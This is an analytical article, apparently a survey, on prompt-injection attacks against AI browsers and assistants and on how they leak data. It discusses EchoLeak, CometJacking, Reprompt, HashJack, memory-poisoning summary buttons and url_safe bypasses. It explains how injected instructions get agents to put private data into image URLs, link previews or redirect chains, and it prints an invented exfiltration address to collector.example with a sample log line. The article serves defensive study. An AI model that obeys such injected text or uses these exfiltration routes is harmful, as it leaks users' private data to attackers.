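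OpenAI trained a new version of the agent to resist these attacks and gave it to all Atlas users. The company can see the agent's private reasoning and outside attackers can't, so it hopes to find weaknesses before they do. It gives no attack success rates from before or after the update, so outsiders can't judge how much the training helped. OpenAI expects that prompt injection, like fraud against people, will probably never be fully solved.

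The highest success rate comes from an academic test of fake login requests. In *LoginTrap*, Guo, Zhang and colleagues (2026) copied 80 real web pages and added a pop-up to each, with a message that made logging in seem necessary to continue. A language model wrote the message to suit the page rather than the user's task. Two other model-based checks predicted whether an agent would fall for the message, and the program revised it if they predicted that the agent would not. An agent that clicked the login button reached a form that asked for private information.

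The researchers ran 1,175 ordinary tasks, such as finding or comparing information on a page, with four models: GPT-4o, Gemini 3 Flash, Claude Sonnet 4 and DeepSeek-V3.2. On average, the agents clicked the fake login button in 93% of tasks and entered private information in 86%. GPT-4o and DeepSeek-V3.2 more often clicked without then giving away information, but mostly because they left the form incomplete, stopped early or returned to the original task. An agent that is better at completing tasks can therefore be more likely to leak private information. With up to nine attempts per page, every model leaked information at least once on each of the 80 pages.

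Guo and colleagues gave the agent invented personal data along with its task and ran everything on a local test system. A real attacker would also have to lead the agent to the copied page and get past any protections in the commercial product. Most of the models were old by the time the paper appeared, so the 86% does not contradict Anthropic's much lower figures for Opus 5. The 86% does show that the 1.6% from real websites is a poor guide to what a determined attacker could achieve, since the injections in that sample were mostly crude orders that nobody had tuned to the page.

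Less polished attacks have succeeded against commercial products. The security firm LayerX built a web page posing as a puzzle game in which wrong answers count as right. Android Authority's *AI browsers were tricked into revealing passwords with a shockingly simple approach* (2026) describes how the game first gets the agent to accept that 2 + 2 does not equal 4, then sends it to another page to find and copy a "hidden code", which is really the user's private data. LayerX calls the technique BioShocking, after a video game whose hero is manipulated into accepting a false reality. ThaiCERT's *Researchers Discover New BioShocking Attack That Tricks AI Browsers* describes a version whose last stage sends the agent to copy passwords from a GitHub repository, an online storage space for software code.

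LayerX tested ChatGPT Atlas, Perplexity's Comet, Fellou, Genspark Browser, Sigma Browser and Anthropic's Claude extension for Chrome, and says all six exposed sensitive information. This means the attack worked at least once on each product, which is not the same as a 100% success rate. LayerX is also the source for how the companies responded after it notified them between October 2025 and January 2026. Android Authority reports that OpenAI fixed the problem in Atlas and that Anthropic tried to fix its extension, but LayerX says the patch failed. Perplexity closed the report without making a change, and the makers of Fellou, Genspark and Sigma did not reply.

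## How can data leak through a link that nobody clicks?

Software often requests web addresses without a click. A browser does this to load images, a chat app to preview a link, and an agent when it uses its own web tool. In each case, injected text has to make the model write an address that contains private data. Ordinary software then sends the data out when it requests that address.

Suppose that Anna, whose email address is anna@mail.example, asks an assistant to summarise a hostile page. The assistant knows her email address, and the page gets the model to write an address like this invented one:

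`https://collector.example/dot.png?d=anna%40mail.example`

In a web address, `%40` stands for the @ sign. When a program requests the address, the server at `collector.example` adds a line to its log:

`203.0.113.7 - - [07/Oct/2026:09:14:02 +0000] "GET /dot.png?d=anna%40mail.example HTTP/1.1" 200 43`

The attacker can now read Anna's email address in the log. If `dot.png` did not exist, the server would return an error and still log the request.

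### An image that the browser loads

In Markdown, an image is written like a link with an exclamation mark in front. A browser waits for a click before it opens a link, but it normally loads an image as soon as it displays the answer. If the model writes the address above as an image, Anna's browser sends her email address to the attacker, and she might notice only a broken picture.

This happened in EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, which answers employees' questions using their organisation's emails, files and chats. Ravia (2025) explains how the attack worked in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*. The team he leads, then called Aim Labs and now part of Cato, found the vulnerability.

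1. The attacker emails an employee. The instructions in the email read as if they were meant for a person and never mention AI, so Microsoft's filter for prompt injection lets them through.
2. The employee later asks Copilot about something at work. Copilot searches for relevant material and retrieves the email.
3. Copilot follows the instructions, picks out the most sensitive information in its context window and adds it to an address on the attacker's server.
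4. Copilot writes the address as an image. Microsoft removed ordinary links and images that pointed to outside sites, but missed a form of Markdown that puts the address on a separate line.
5. The employee's browser tries to load the image. Copilot's page has an allowlist, a list of sites from which it may load images, and the attacker's server is not on it. The image address therefore points to a Microsoft Teams service that is on the list and fetches other addresses on request.
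6. The Teams service fetches the attacker's address, and the stolen information appears in the attacker's log.

Security researchers call this a zero-click attack because nobody has to click a malicious link. It works during ordinary use of the assistant, when the employee asks Copilot a question that makes it retrieve the email. To make retrieval more likely, Aim Labs wrote one long email with headings such as staff onboarding and leave of absence, and repeated the instructions under each, so that questions on many topics would match some part of it. The email also told its reader never to refer to it, so Copilot's answer didn't name it as a source.

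Aim Labs developed the zero-click attack in stages. The first version showed the employee a link to click. The second used an image loaded through SharePoint, Microsoft's file-sharing service, but worked only if the employee had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. The final version used Teams and needed no invitation. The attack could expose anything in Copilot's context window, including earlier messages in the chat and files that Copilot had retrieved.

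Microsoft rated the flaw 9.3 out of 10 for severity, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). Reddy and Gujral (2025) report in *EchoLeak* that Aim Labs disclosed the flaw privately in January 2025, Microsoft fixed it in May, and the public announcement followed in June. Microsoft found no evidence that anyone had used the flaw against customers. Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first "real-world" attack of its kind, by which they mean that it worked on a commercial product.

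It is debatable how new the chain was. Willison (2025) calls it an extended variant of leaks that people had already found in a dozen products. However, it did get past four safeguards: the filter on incoming text, the removal of links, the allowlist and the naming of sources.

Aim Labs is less consistent about whether customers could have protected themselves. Ravia writes that, as far as the team knows, no administrator setting could have prevented the attack. But Aim Labs' *EchoLeak*, a Q&A page, says organisations can configure Copilot to ignore emails from outside. That setting would have kept the attacker's email out of the context window, but it would also have stopped Copilot from answering questions about emails from an organisation's own customers. Aim Labs also promotes its own product as protection on both pages.

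### The same exit a year later

In June 2026 the security firm Varonis described another leak from Microsoft 365 Copilot, this time in its enterprise search (*SearchLeak*, 2026). The attack started with one click on a genuine Microsoft link that contained the attacker's instructions in place of a search query. The data then leaked without another click.

Copilot searched the victim's mailbox and wrote an image address containing the title of an email. Microsoft's safeguard turned the answer into plain text so that no image could load, but only after Copilot had finished writing. The browser displayed the answer as it arrived, so it requested the image before the safeguard took effect. The allowlist again blocked the attacker's server but included Bing, whose image search fetches pictures from other sites. Bing fetched the attacker's address with the email title in its path. In Varonis's example,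 the title contained a security code, which an attacker could try to use before it expired.

Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) confirms that the flaw let an outsider obtain information. Microsoft classes the flaw as critical but scored it at only 6.5 out of 10. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* attributes the lower score to the click that the attack required. Microsoft records no exploitation and says it has fully fixed the problem on its own servers. The advisory doesn't describe how the attack worked, so the details about timing and Bing's role come from Varonis.

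In both attacks the allowlist worked as Microsoft had configured it. The browser contacted only approved sites, but one of them passed the data on. An allowlist therefore has to exclude any service that fetches URLs for anyone who asks, even if the service belongs to the same company as the assistant.

An image can also load somewhere the user never looks. In *OpenAI API Logs*, the security firm PromptArmor built a mock application that helps a bank check its customers' identities. One of the application's six sources of information contained injected text, and the model wrote an image address containing a customer's personal and financial details. A second model flagged the answer, and the application never displayed it. But when a developer opened the conversation in OpenAI's log viewer to find out why, the viewer displayed the blocked answer with its image, and the developer's browser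 sent the customer's details to the attacker.

PromptArmor reported this flaw in November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that screens such reports for OpenAI. The report was still marked "not applicable" when PromptArmor published its findings. OpenAI then confirmed the flaw, reopened the report on 22 January 2026 and said it was working on a fix. Blocking images in the application itself would not have prevented this leak, because the image loaded in OpenAI's product.

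### A preview that a chat app fetches

Many people now talk to AI agents through messaging apps. These apps often preview a link by automatically fetching its address and showing a title or picture. When an agent posts a link, injected text may have influenced the address that the app fetches.

Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, described the risk of data leaking through link previews in Slack and Discord. PromptArmor demonstrated it in 2026 with OpenClaw, an agent that people can use through several messaging apps. In PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, the agent reads a source that contains injected text and replies to its user with a link to the attacker's site, with the user's data in the query string. The messaging app fetches the link for a preview as soon as the reply arrives, so the attacker can read the data in the site's log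 even if the user recognises the link as suspicious and deletes the message.

The log entry usually looks different from one that an image leaves. PromptArmor recorded visits from programs such as Slackbot, which fetch pages for the messaging company.

PromptArmor found that OpenClaw could leak data through link previews on Telegram under the default settings. The data stopped arriving when PromptArmor turned off previews in OpenClaw's configuration file. PromptArmor also set up a public website where people can test their own combination of agent and app, see what a preview request carried and report the result. Apostol's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* lists Slack, Discord and Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio among the affected platforms.

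These results come from PromptArmor and volunteers, so they can't show what share of agents is exposed. The test also checks only whether an app fetches a link the agent has already written. How often injected text would get the agent to write such a link depends on the model.

This leak can be closed with unusually little inconvenience to users, who lose only a thumbnail and a title when link previews are off. Software that posts messages to Slack can switch off previews for its own messages, as Willison reports from the security researcher Johann Rehberger. But this only works if the messaging company offers the setting and the agent's developer uses it. PromptArmor would like messaging apps to let people turn off previews for individual chats, so that a conversation with an agent could have stricter settings than one with friends.

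Previews can also leak data from a message that only the user receives. According to Microsoft's documentation, Copilot Cowork, an agent that works across a company's systems, will ask permission before sending an email or posting in Teams. PromptArmor reports that the agent did not ask when the recipient was the user. An app that fetches the links in such a message can send data to a stranger, so the message may need approval even though nobody else receives it.

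### A request from the agent's own web tool

An agent with a web tool can leak data without showing the user an address. The agent requests the address while it is working, and the user sees only an ordinary summary. Paul's attack on Claude used this method to spell out a user's name one letter at a time.

The request may leave no trace on the user's equipment, depending on the product. In ShadowLeak, an attack on ChatGPT's research agent, the request came from the provider's servers, so a company that monitored only its employees' browsers and computers could have missed it.

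Varonis found a leak of this kind in the consumer version of Copilot, according to an account that the Cloud Security Alliance republished. A safeguard removed private data from an address before Copilot fetched it, but only on the first request. When the testers told Copilot to do everything twice, the second request leaked their secret phrase. The user had to click a link to start the attack, but it continued even if they closed the Copilot tab.

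### How often a small agent leaked in a controlled test

In *Silent Egress*, eBay researchers Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) measured this kind of leak by recording the requests that an agent made. They built the agent on the 7-billion-parameter version of Qwen 2.5 and ran everything on their own machines. They put invented secrets, such as an access key, directly into the agent's context window. The user always asked the agent to summarise a page, and the page contained an instruction to send the secret to a server that the researchers controlled.

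The researchers varied whether the instruction appeared in the page's title, its metadata, its body or the text of a link. They also varied whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects, which send a visitor on from one address to another, and whether the instruction asked for the secret in one request or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs.

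A request reached the researchers' server in 423 runs, or 88.1%. In 95% of these successful attacks, the final answer looked harmless, so a safety check that read only the answers would have missed them. The agent never contacted the server in 120 further runs with harmless pages, but this control is weaker than it sounds because those pages did not give the agent the server's address.

Splitting the secret into pieces made the attack succeed less often, while the hiding place and the redirects made little difference. When the instruction asked for a single request, one reached the server in 238 of 240 runs (99%). When it asked for four pieces, the figure fell to 185 of 240 (77%). The model had to keep track of the pieces and make several requests in order, which gave it more chances to fail.

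Lan and colleagues present splitting as a way to avoid detection, because a filter that looks for a complete password won't recognise four characters of it. Their numbers don't establish how well this works. They use a measure called Leak@k, the share of runs in which at least one of the first *k* requests contains sensitive data:

`Leak@k = runs with sensitive data in any of the first k requests / all runs`

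Leak@3 can never be lower than Leak@1, because a leak in the first request is also a leak in the first three. But for split secrets, the paper reports a Leak@1 of 0.263 and a Leak@3 of 0.158. Either at least one of these figures is wrong, or the researchers calculated them in a way they don't describe.

The interpretation has a second problem. The paper counts even a fragment of the secret as sensitive data, so a low Leak@1 would mean that the first request usually carried none of the secret. That would make the attack less successful rather than harder to detect. The total of 423 runs does not depend on Leak@1, but it counts runs in which a request reached the server, whether or not the request contained the secret. The two counts nearly agree for single-request attacks, where the first request contained sensitive data in 96.7% of runs.

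### Which defences stopped the requests

Lan and colleagues then tested defences against one version of the attack, with the instruction in the page's body and the secret in a single request. They ran each condition 30 times.

| Defence | Runs in which the agent attempted a request | Leak rate |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 1.000 |
| System prompt that forbids following web content | 66.7% | 0.667 |
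| Delimiters that mark the page as untrusted | 100% | 1.000 |
| System prompt and delimiters | 56.7% | 0.567 |
| Allowlist of domains | 100% | 0 |
| Blocking of suspicious addresses | 83.3% | 0 |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 23.3% | 0 |
| Filter for random-looking text | 0% | 0 |
| All of the above | 0% | 0 |

The system prompt, the developer's standing instructions to the model, helped somewhat. Delimiters alone had no effect. Using both did better than the system prompt alone by only three runs out of 30, which could easily be chance.

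The allowlist result is the clearest, because the agent attempted a request in every run and the software blocked every one. This defence works even when the injection has taken over the model. But the list contained only four domains, three of which belonged to a fictional company, and the attacker's domain obviously did not belong with them. An assistant that has to open any page its user asks about can't work with such a short list. The researchers also warn that an attacker could send data through a legitimate site that forwards visitors elsewhere. EchoLeak and SearchLeak both got around an allowlist in a similar way.

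The zeros for the other filters are less reliable. The rule for suspicious addresses blocked any path containing certain words, including "collect". The paper's example attacks use a path with that name, but a real attacker would choose another word.

The two filters that inspect the contents of an address act after the model has written its request, so they should change how many requests get through and leave the number of attempts about the same. Instead, attempts fell from 100% to 23.3% with the word filter and to zero with the filter for random-looking text. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided random-looking text when that filter was active, but they describe no way for information about the filter to reach the model. For the word filter, they suggest that the model sometimes rewrote the secret in another form, but those requests should then have passed the filter and reached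 the server, and none did. Until someone explains the drop in attempts, a leak rate of zero is poor evidence that these filters work.

Lan and colleagues describe their success rates as a lower bound because they used simple, undisguised instructions. They also acknowledge that their set-up favoured the attacker, because the secret was already in the context window, the system prompt contained little beyond instructions for using the tool, and the software passed on page text without cleaning it. These choices push the rate in opposite directions, so 88.1% is neither a lower nor an upper bound for commercial products. The experiment does show that an agent can leak data while giving a normal answer.

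### How much the model matters

Lan and colleagues, who tested only one model, argue that more capable models might be more vulnerable because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably. Rall, Bauer and colleagues (2025) had tried a similar attack on 28 models in *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* and found no clear relationship between size and vulnerability.

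The researchers' agent could fetch web pages and search a fictional company's internal documents, which contained a secret code. The user asked it to summarise a blog post that contained an instruction, in white text on a white background, to look up the code, add it to a web address and request that address. The researchers tested each model with 89 versions of this instruction, each in its original form and in 11 altered forms, such as a Hindi translation or a copy with random capital letters, for a total of 1,068 attempts per model.

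xAI's Grok 4 leaked the secret in 72.4% of attempts, and the largest Qwen3 model leaked it in 28.3%. Half of the models leaked it in at most 1.4% of attempts, and six never did, including Claude Sonnet 4 and GPT-5 nano. The researchers attribute OpenAI's low rates to training its models to rank a developer's or user's instructions above text from a tool, but the experiment did not test that explanation. They also observe that models from the same company tend to have similar rates, although two other xAI models leaked the secret in only 4.5% and 8.2% of attempts.

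One of the 28 models was the 72-billion-parameter version of Qwen 2.5, a larger relative of the model in the eBay test. It leaked the secret in 5.2% of attempts, against 99% for the smaller version when the eBay researchers asked for a single request. Size is only one possible reason for the difference. Rall and colleagues' agent had to find the secret before it could send it, and many of their altered instructions were hard for any model to follow. For example, no model carried out an instruction written in binary code, yet those failures count in every model's average. The unaltered instructions worked more often, in over 12% of attempts across all models.

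Rall and colleagues ran each attempt only once and added no defences beyond the models' own training. All the models date from 2025 or earlier, so the ranking is a poor guide to current products. Still, with the same tools and the same hostile page, the leak rate ranged from zero to nearly three in four depending on the model, and a user who asks for a summary may not know which model the assistant is running.

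## What can a user's own click set off?

A link in an assistant's answer can take the user to an attacker's site. A link in an email or on a web page can open the assistant with the attacker's instructions already in place, so clicking it starts the attack.

### A false alert in a summary

*ChatGPhish*, published by the security firm Permiso in May 2026, describes how a web page can add a phishing link to ChatGPT's reply. The researchers tested the attack on a README, the page that introduces a software project on GitHub. They added text that presented a false account alert as part of the required format for every summary. They then opened the page in Firefox and chose the menu option to summarise it with ChatGPT. ChatGPT wrote a genuine summary of the project, followed by a notice about a new device on the user's account and a clickable link to an outside site.

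The user would have seen one continuous reply, with no sign that the alert came from the README. The researchers got the same result with a page they built about Kosovo, so the attack does not depend on GitHub. They show the attack in screenshots but give no success rate.

In another version, the reply contained a QR code, which loaded as an image from the researchers' online storage. A user who scans the code with a phone opens the attacker's site on the phone. The computer's browser never handles the address, so the user can't check it by hovering over a link, the browser can't compare it with a list of known phishing sites, and a password manager on the computer can't detect that the domain is wrong. Many phones show the address before opening it, but the user has to spot the problem unaided.

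The researchers also used an image only for tracking, which required no click or scan. Its address belonged to a link-shortening service, which forwarded the request to their server. The server recorded the network address of the machine that requested the image, the browser type, the exact time and, in some cases, the referring page.

None of this came from the conversation, because the image address was the same for every reader and so could not contain anything a particular user had told ChatGPT. To leak a conversation, the injected text would have had to make the model write a new address containing the private data, as EchoLeak did with Copilot. Permiso did not demonstrate that, although the title of its first report to OpenAI included the words "data exfiltration".

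An attacker who runs the summarised page already receives the user's network address and browser type when the user opens the page. The image adds only that the user asked ChatGPT about the page, and when. The attacker learns more from the image on a site like GitHub, where outsiders can write a page's text but can't read the server's log.

Permiso reported the problem to OpenAI through Bugcrowd on 29 April 2026. OpenAI replied the next day that it could not reproduce the attack from the details provided. On 1 May the researchers sent a fuller report, which was labelled "not applicable" and later "duplicate", meaning that someone had already reported the issue. On 7 May they asked for further discussion, and on 29 May they published. Two days later, eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* concluded from this timeline that OpenAI had apparently not fixed the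 problem. It is unclear whether OpenAI has fixed it since.

### Why the image may have loaded

OpenAI had already published a link check meant to stop ChatGPT from automatically opening addresses that might carry a user's data. The check doesn't apply to the phishing link, because the user opens it in their own browser, but the image loaded automatically.

One possible explanation is that the image address from the README looked to ChatGPT like one the user had supplied. Firefox puts a page's text into the user's own message to the chatbot, as ERNW's attack on page titles showed, and ChatGPT reportedly treats addresses in the user's messages as safe, on the reasonable assumption that the user chose them. This explanation is an inference, because Permiso says only that Firefox passes the page's content to ChatGPT and does not discuss the link check.

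Another explanation, also unconfirmed, is that a check for private data in addresses has little reason to block an image address that is the same for everybody, especially if a crawler has already seen it on a public page. In that case the check would have worked as OpenAI intended, and tracking by image would be outside its scope.

Whether Firefox is partly at fault depends on which of the two explanations is right. Permiso says the attack does not exploit a flaw in Firefox, because ChatGPT decides how to display the answer. That is fair for the missing label on the phishing link. But if the first explanation is right, Firefox contributed to the image loading by presenting a stranger's text as the user's.

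### Trust in links that an assistant shows

People would probably trust the link more in ChatGPT's reply than on the original page. An alert about a ChatGPT account looks out of place in a software project's README, but users would expect to see one in ChatGPT. The alert also followed a useful summary that the user had requested. And a reader who knows that strangers write web pages may still think of the reply as ChatGPT's own work.

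No published study appears to have compared how often people click the same link on a web page and in an assistant's answer. Experiments on related questions give some indirect evidence.

In *Citations and Trust in LLM Generated Responses* (2025), participants asked a chatbot questions and rated how much they trusted its answers. They trusted answers with citations more than answers without them, and accurate citations more than random ones. Participants who checked the citations tended to give lower ratings. Checking may have exposed bad citations, or people who already doubted an answer may have been more likely to check. Participants also chose their own questions, which makes their ratings harder to compare.

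A larger experiment, *Human Trust in AI Search* (2025), looked for signs that people notice when an answer's references are invalid. Participants who received references spent more time on their first search task and clicked more, so the researchers expected them to notice bad links there. But invalid links in the first task did not significantly predict how much participants trusted that answer or later ones. This suggests that extra time and clicks are not enough to make bad links stand out, though some participants may have noticed them.

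Even users who notice bad advice may follow it, as the title of *I know it's not right, but that's what it said to do* (2025) suggests. In that study, participants worked through five cybersecurity tasks with a chatbot. For the last two, the researchers secretly switched to a model trained to give bad advice.

None of these experiments used a phishing link. An invalid reference does little harm if the reader ignores it. Unlike most references, a security alert urges the reader to act, which might make people click more often or make them suspicious.

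### Instructions after the "#" of a genuine address

A phishing link can also appear in an assistant's answer while the user is on a genuine website. In *HashJack*, Simonovich (2025) describes how his team at Cato put instructions in the fragment of a web address. An attacker could send such a link to a bank's customer. Clicking it only opens the bank's real, unaltered page. When the customer then asks the browser's assistant a question, such as what new services the bank offers, the browser gives the assistant the full address, including the attacker's instructions.

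The user can see the instructions in the address bar, but only by reading to the end of a long address at a site they have good reason to trust. Browsers don't send fragments to servers, so the bank can't see the instructions, and a company that inspects its employees' network traffic would miss them too.

Simonovich tested the attack on demonstration sites. Cato first reported it on 30 July 2025, to Perplexity. In some tests, the injected text added a false support number or a fake login link to the answer. In another, when the user asked about a loan, Comet sent account details and transactions to an outside server in the background.

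| Assistant | False text in the answer | What happened with the attacker's link | Data sent in the background |
|---|---|---|---|
| Comet | Yes | It appeared as a live link | Yes |
| Copilot in Edge | Yes | The browser asked for confirmation before opening it | Not observed |
| Gemini in Chrome | Yes | Chrome often turned it into a Google search | Not observed |

The same prompts failed on Claude for Chrome and ChatGPT Atlas. Microsoft said it had fixed the problem in Edge by 27 October 2025. Bugcrowd, which also handles reports for Perplexity, closed the case in August as "not applicable", then reopened it when Cato sent more examples. In October Perplexity rated the flaw as critical and acknowledged that it had mishandled the report. It applied its final fix on 18 November.

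Google reproduced the behaviour within two days but classed it as intended, and had not changed it when Cato published on 25 November. Google's low rating is easier to understand for Gemini than it would be for Comet, because Gemini never sent data anywhere in these tests. But a false answer can do harm without a link. In one test, the instructions made the assistants state an altered dose for a medicine while the user was on a page about it.

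Simonovich argues that the attack is far more likely to succeed than ordinary phishing because the site is genuine. That is plausible for the same reasons as with ChatGPhish, but Cato tested browsers, not people.

### Links that write the user's request

Many assistants accept a request in the query string of their own web address, as in the invented link `https://assistant.example/?q=What+is+the+weather+today`. Opening the link fills the message box with the question, and some assistants also submit it at once. This is useful for bookmarks and shortcuts, but anyone can write such a link and send it to someone else.

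The assistant then receives the attacker's text as the user's own message. Training a model to rank the user's words above those of a web page gives no protection here, and may help the attacker.

ChatGPT used to submit prompts in a link's `?q=` parameter without asking the user to confirm. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025) explains that a link could contain instructions for ChatGPT to change how it replied and save that change in its memory. The link could also contain a request to summarise a hostile page, so one click led to indirect prompt injection.

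The security firm Tenable reported the flaw on 15 April 2025, and OpenAI released a fix to all users by the end of the month. On 6 May Tenable found that the problem persisted. OpenAI said on 11 July that it had added a new protection based on a label that browsers attach to each request, which shows whether the request started on another site. This lets ChatGPT treat a link clicked on another site differently from an address the user typed.

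### CometJacking

LayerX, which also devised the BioShocking puzzle, found a more damaging version in Perplexity's Comet. In CometJacking, the user clicks a link in an email or on a web page, and Comet reads part of the address as a request to its assistant. LayerX found that adding a second value that Perplexity didn't recognise to the address made the assistant search its memory of the user instead of the web.

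In the request, the attacker tells the assistant to send them information from the user's email or calendar. Perplexity had a safeguard against sending sensitive data, but it missed data in base64, a standard way of writing any file as letters, digits and a few symbols. Anyone can decode base64. The assistant then ran a short program that sent the encoded data in the body of a web request, as a form does. The address therefore did not need to contain any private data, so a check of the address alone would not have detected the leak.

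According to LayerX, the user saw what looked like an ordinary question to the assistant and never had to enter a password, because Comet already had permission to read the accounts. LayerX is less clear about how much data an attacker could take. Its summary refers to emails and appointments that the assistant had helped to write, while its account of the tests refers to copying all the messages in a connected mailbox, which would expose far more.

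The companies also disagree about how Perplexity handled the report. LayerX reported the flaw on 27 August 2025 and says Perplexity replied that it could see no security impact. The Hacker News (2025) repeated that assessment when it covered the attack in October. But Perplexity told TIME that the report was poorly worded and that LayerX had not answered requests for clarification. Perplexity also said that nobody had exploited the flaw and that it had later found the flaw independently and fixed it, though it is the only source for the fix.

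PromptArmor, Cato and Permiso also had reports marked "not applicable" at some stage. Perplexity later rated Cato's report as critical and OpenAI reopened PromptArmor's, so the label is poor evidence that a flaw is harmless.

### One click on a genuine Copilot link

Varonis' *Reprompt* describes an attack that worked on the consumer version of Microsoft's Copilot. It used a link to Copilot's real website with a request in the query string. When the user clicked the link, Copilot immediately ran the request in the user's logged-in session. The user saw a Copilot page open, and closing it did not stop the request.

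Copilot would not usually fetch an address without a good reason, so the researchers presented the task as a puzzle about identifying a bird in a picture. To solve it, Copilot had to put the user's name into the picture's address and open it. The researchers made Copilot do this twice because its safeguard covered only the first request.

The attacker's server could then reply with further instructions. In the researchers' example, the server requested in turn the user's local time, their location, everything Copilot had learned about them and a summary of their last conversation. Copilot sent each answer inside the next address it opened. An attacker could also adapt the requests, such as by asking for more detail after learning where the user worked.

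Varonis tells users to read any request that appears automatically before they run it, but Reprompt gave them no time to do so. Even studying the link in advance would have revealed little about what the attacker would take, because the server sent most of the instructions later.

*Microsoft Copilot Reprompt Attack Enables Stealthy Data Exfiltration* (Underhill, 2026) reported the attack on 14 January, after Microsoft had fixed it. The attack did not affect Microsoft 365 Copilot, the version for organisations, but SearchLeak later used a similar link against that product.

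Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes another attack on the consumer version. This time the request in the link only filled the message box, and the user had to press Enter to run it. But adding a second, undocumented setting to the address made the request run as soon as the page loaded. The researchers found this setting by repeatedly asking Copilot why a request could not run automatically. Copilot included the setting's name when explaining what Microsoft had disabled, and the researchers tried it and found that it still worked.

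The researchers tested a Copilot account with access to a Gmail mailbox. The link made Copilot find the sender of the latest email, add the sender's email address to a URL and ask for a summary of the resulting page. Opening the page sent the email address to the researchers' server. Copilot also retrieved the full text of an email that contained a password. The user had given Copilot permission to read their email, so neither Gmail nor its connection to Copilot had a flaw, but Copilot could not tell that the request came from someone else.

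United Nations University gives the flaw's severity as 8.8 out of 10. Varonis, which sells data-security products, reported the flaw in December 2025, and Microsoft released its fixes about eight months later, on 18 August 2026. Varonis says it has seen no sign that anyone exploited the flaw.

Requiring the user to press Enter would at least give them a chance to notice a strange request. This would help more against a request to search a mailbox than against one that looks almost exactly like what the user wanted.

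### "Summarize with AI" buttons

Ordinary companies have begun to use these more innocent-looking links. Microsoft (2026) describes buttons labelled "Summarize with AI" on blogs and company websites. Clicking one opens the reader's assistant with a request to summarise the article, as the reader expects, but the request also includes an instruction to remember the company as a trusted source or to cite it in future conversations.

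Over 60 days, Microsoft examined links to AI assistants in email traffic and found 50 different requests of this type from 31 companies. All were real businesses, not scammers, and they worked in more than a dozen industries, including health, finance and legal services. One sold security products. Most of the published examples are requests to treat the site as an authority on some topic, but the most aggressive ones put a full sales pitch into the assistant's memory.

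Microsoft traced the trend to free tools that supply publishers with the code. The promoters of one, CiteMET, describe the technique as a "growth hack" for appearing in AI answers.

The count shows that companies are trying this, but not how well it works. Microsoft doesn't report how many people clicked or how often an assistant stored the instruction, and it says the effect varies between assistants and has changed over time. The count covers links that appeared in emails, so it probably misses many website buttons whose links were never emailed.

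A reader who hovers over the button can see the full address, but web addresses replace spaces with codes such as `%20`, which makes a long request hard to read. The first part is usually an innocent request for a summary, which the reader gets after clicking. In a demonstration with an invented website, the only other trace was a new entry in the assistant's list of saved memories.

Microsoft compares these buttons with adware, software that displays unwanted advertising, because they leave something behind on the user's side without clear awareness or consent. A publisher could argue that they do for AI answers what companies have long done to improve their place in search results. The adware comparison fits in one respect. One company is responsible for a search engine's ranking for everyone who searches, whereas a saved memory affects the later questions of one reader, who asked only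 for a summary and may take the resulting recommendation for independent advice.

Microsoft says several previously reported behaviours no longer work in Copilot. Its protections include filtering known patterns and separating the user's instructions from outside content. That separation is unlikely to help much with these buttons, because the assistant receives the whole request as the user's message. Microsoft makes no similar claim for the other assistants the links target, which include ChatGPT, Claude, Perplexity and Grok.

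A hostile page can make the same kind of change without a button. As part of CoSnitch, the researchers hid instructions in a web page and asked Copilot to summarise it. Copilot returned a normal-looking summary and saved the attacker's text in its memory for that user. In one test, the saved text led Copilot to say that a known security flaw posed no risk. According to Varonis, changing the password or logging out does not remove the saved text. The user has to delete it in the memory settings.

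## Can a system tell which links are safe to open?

In most of the leaks described so far, private data went out as part of a web address. Software could prevent such leaks by checking each address before requesting it. OpenAI has tried several kinds of check since 2023, and outside researchers have repeatedly found ways past them.

### The first check on images

Willison's *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* describes an early public demonstration from April 2023. Roman Samoilenko got ChatGPT to write an image address containing data from the conversation. The image was a single pixel, so the user was unlikely to notice it.

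The security researcher Johann Rehberger also reported the problem to OpenAI in early 2023. In *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red, he recalls that the company showed little interest in fixing it. Bing Chat had the same flaw, and Microsoft responded in May 2023 by generally blocking the chat page from loading images.

In December 2023, OpenAI changed ChatGPT's web page to send an image's address to OpenAI's servers before displaying the image, and a feature called `url_safe` decided whether it could load. Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, called this "half-baked" because OpenAI could have blocked all images from outside sites instead. He expected attackers to get past the check by hiding data in a subdomain or file name. The iPhone app did not have the check.

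OpenAI did not explain how `url_safe` reached its decisions. Rehberger worked out parts of it by experiment and presented ways around it at the Black Hat Europe conference in 2024. Tenable's *HackedGPT*, published in November 2025, lists some of the factors the company's researchers identified, including whether OpenAI trusted the domain, whether the address had a subdomain or a query string, and what the conversation contained. By then the check also covered ordinary links, and ChatGPT left out any that failed.

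### Trusted sites that pass data on

Tenable found that addresses on `bing.com` always passed ChatGPT's `url_safe` check. Each Bing search result has its own `bing.com` address, which forwards the visitor to the listed site. Anyone whose site appeared in Bing's results therefore had an address that ChatGPT trusted and that led to their own server. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) calls this "an open redirect as a service". An open redirect is a page on one site that forwards visitors to an address of someone else's choosing.

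Bing links cannot be altered, so the researchers couldn't add a user's data to one. Instead, they got Bing to index a separate page for each letter of the alphabet. Injected text could then make ChatGPT display the matching links as images, in the order that spelled out the user's data. Each link was the same for every user, and only the sequence contained private data.

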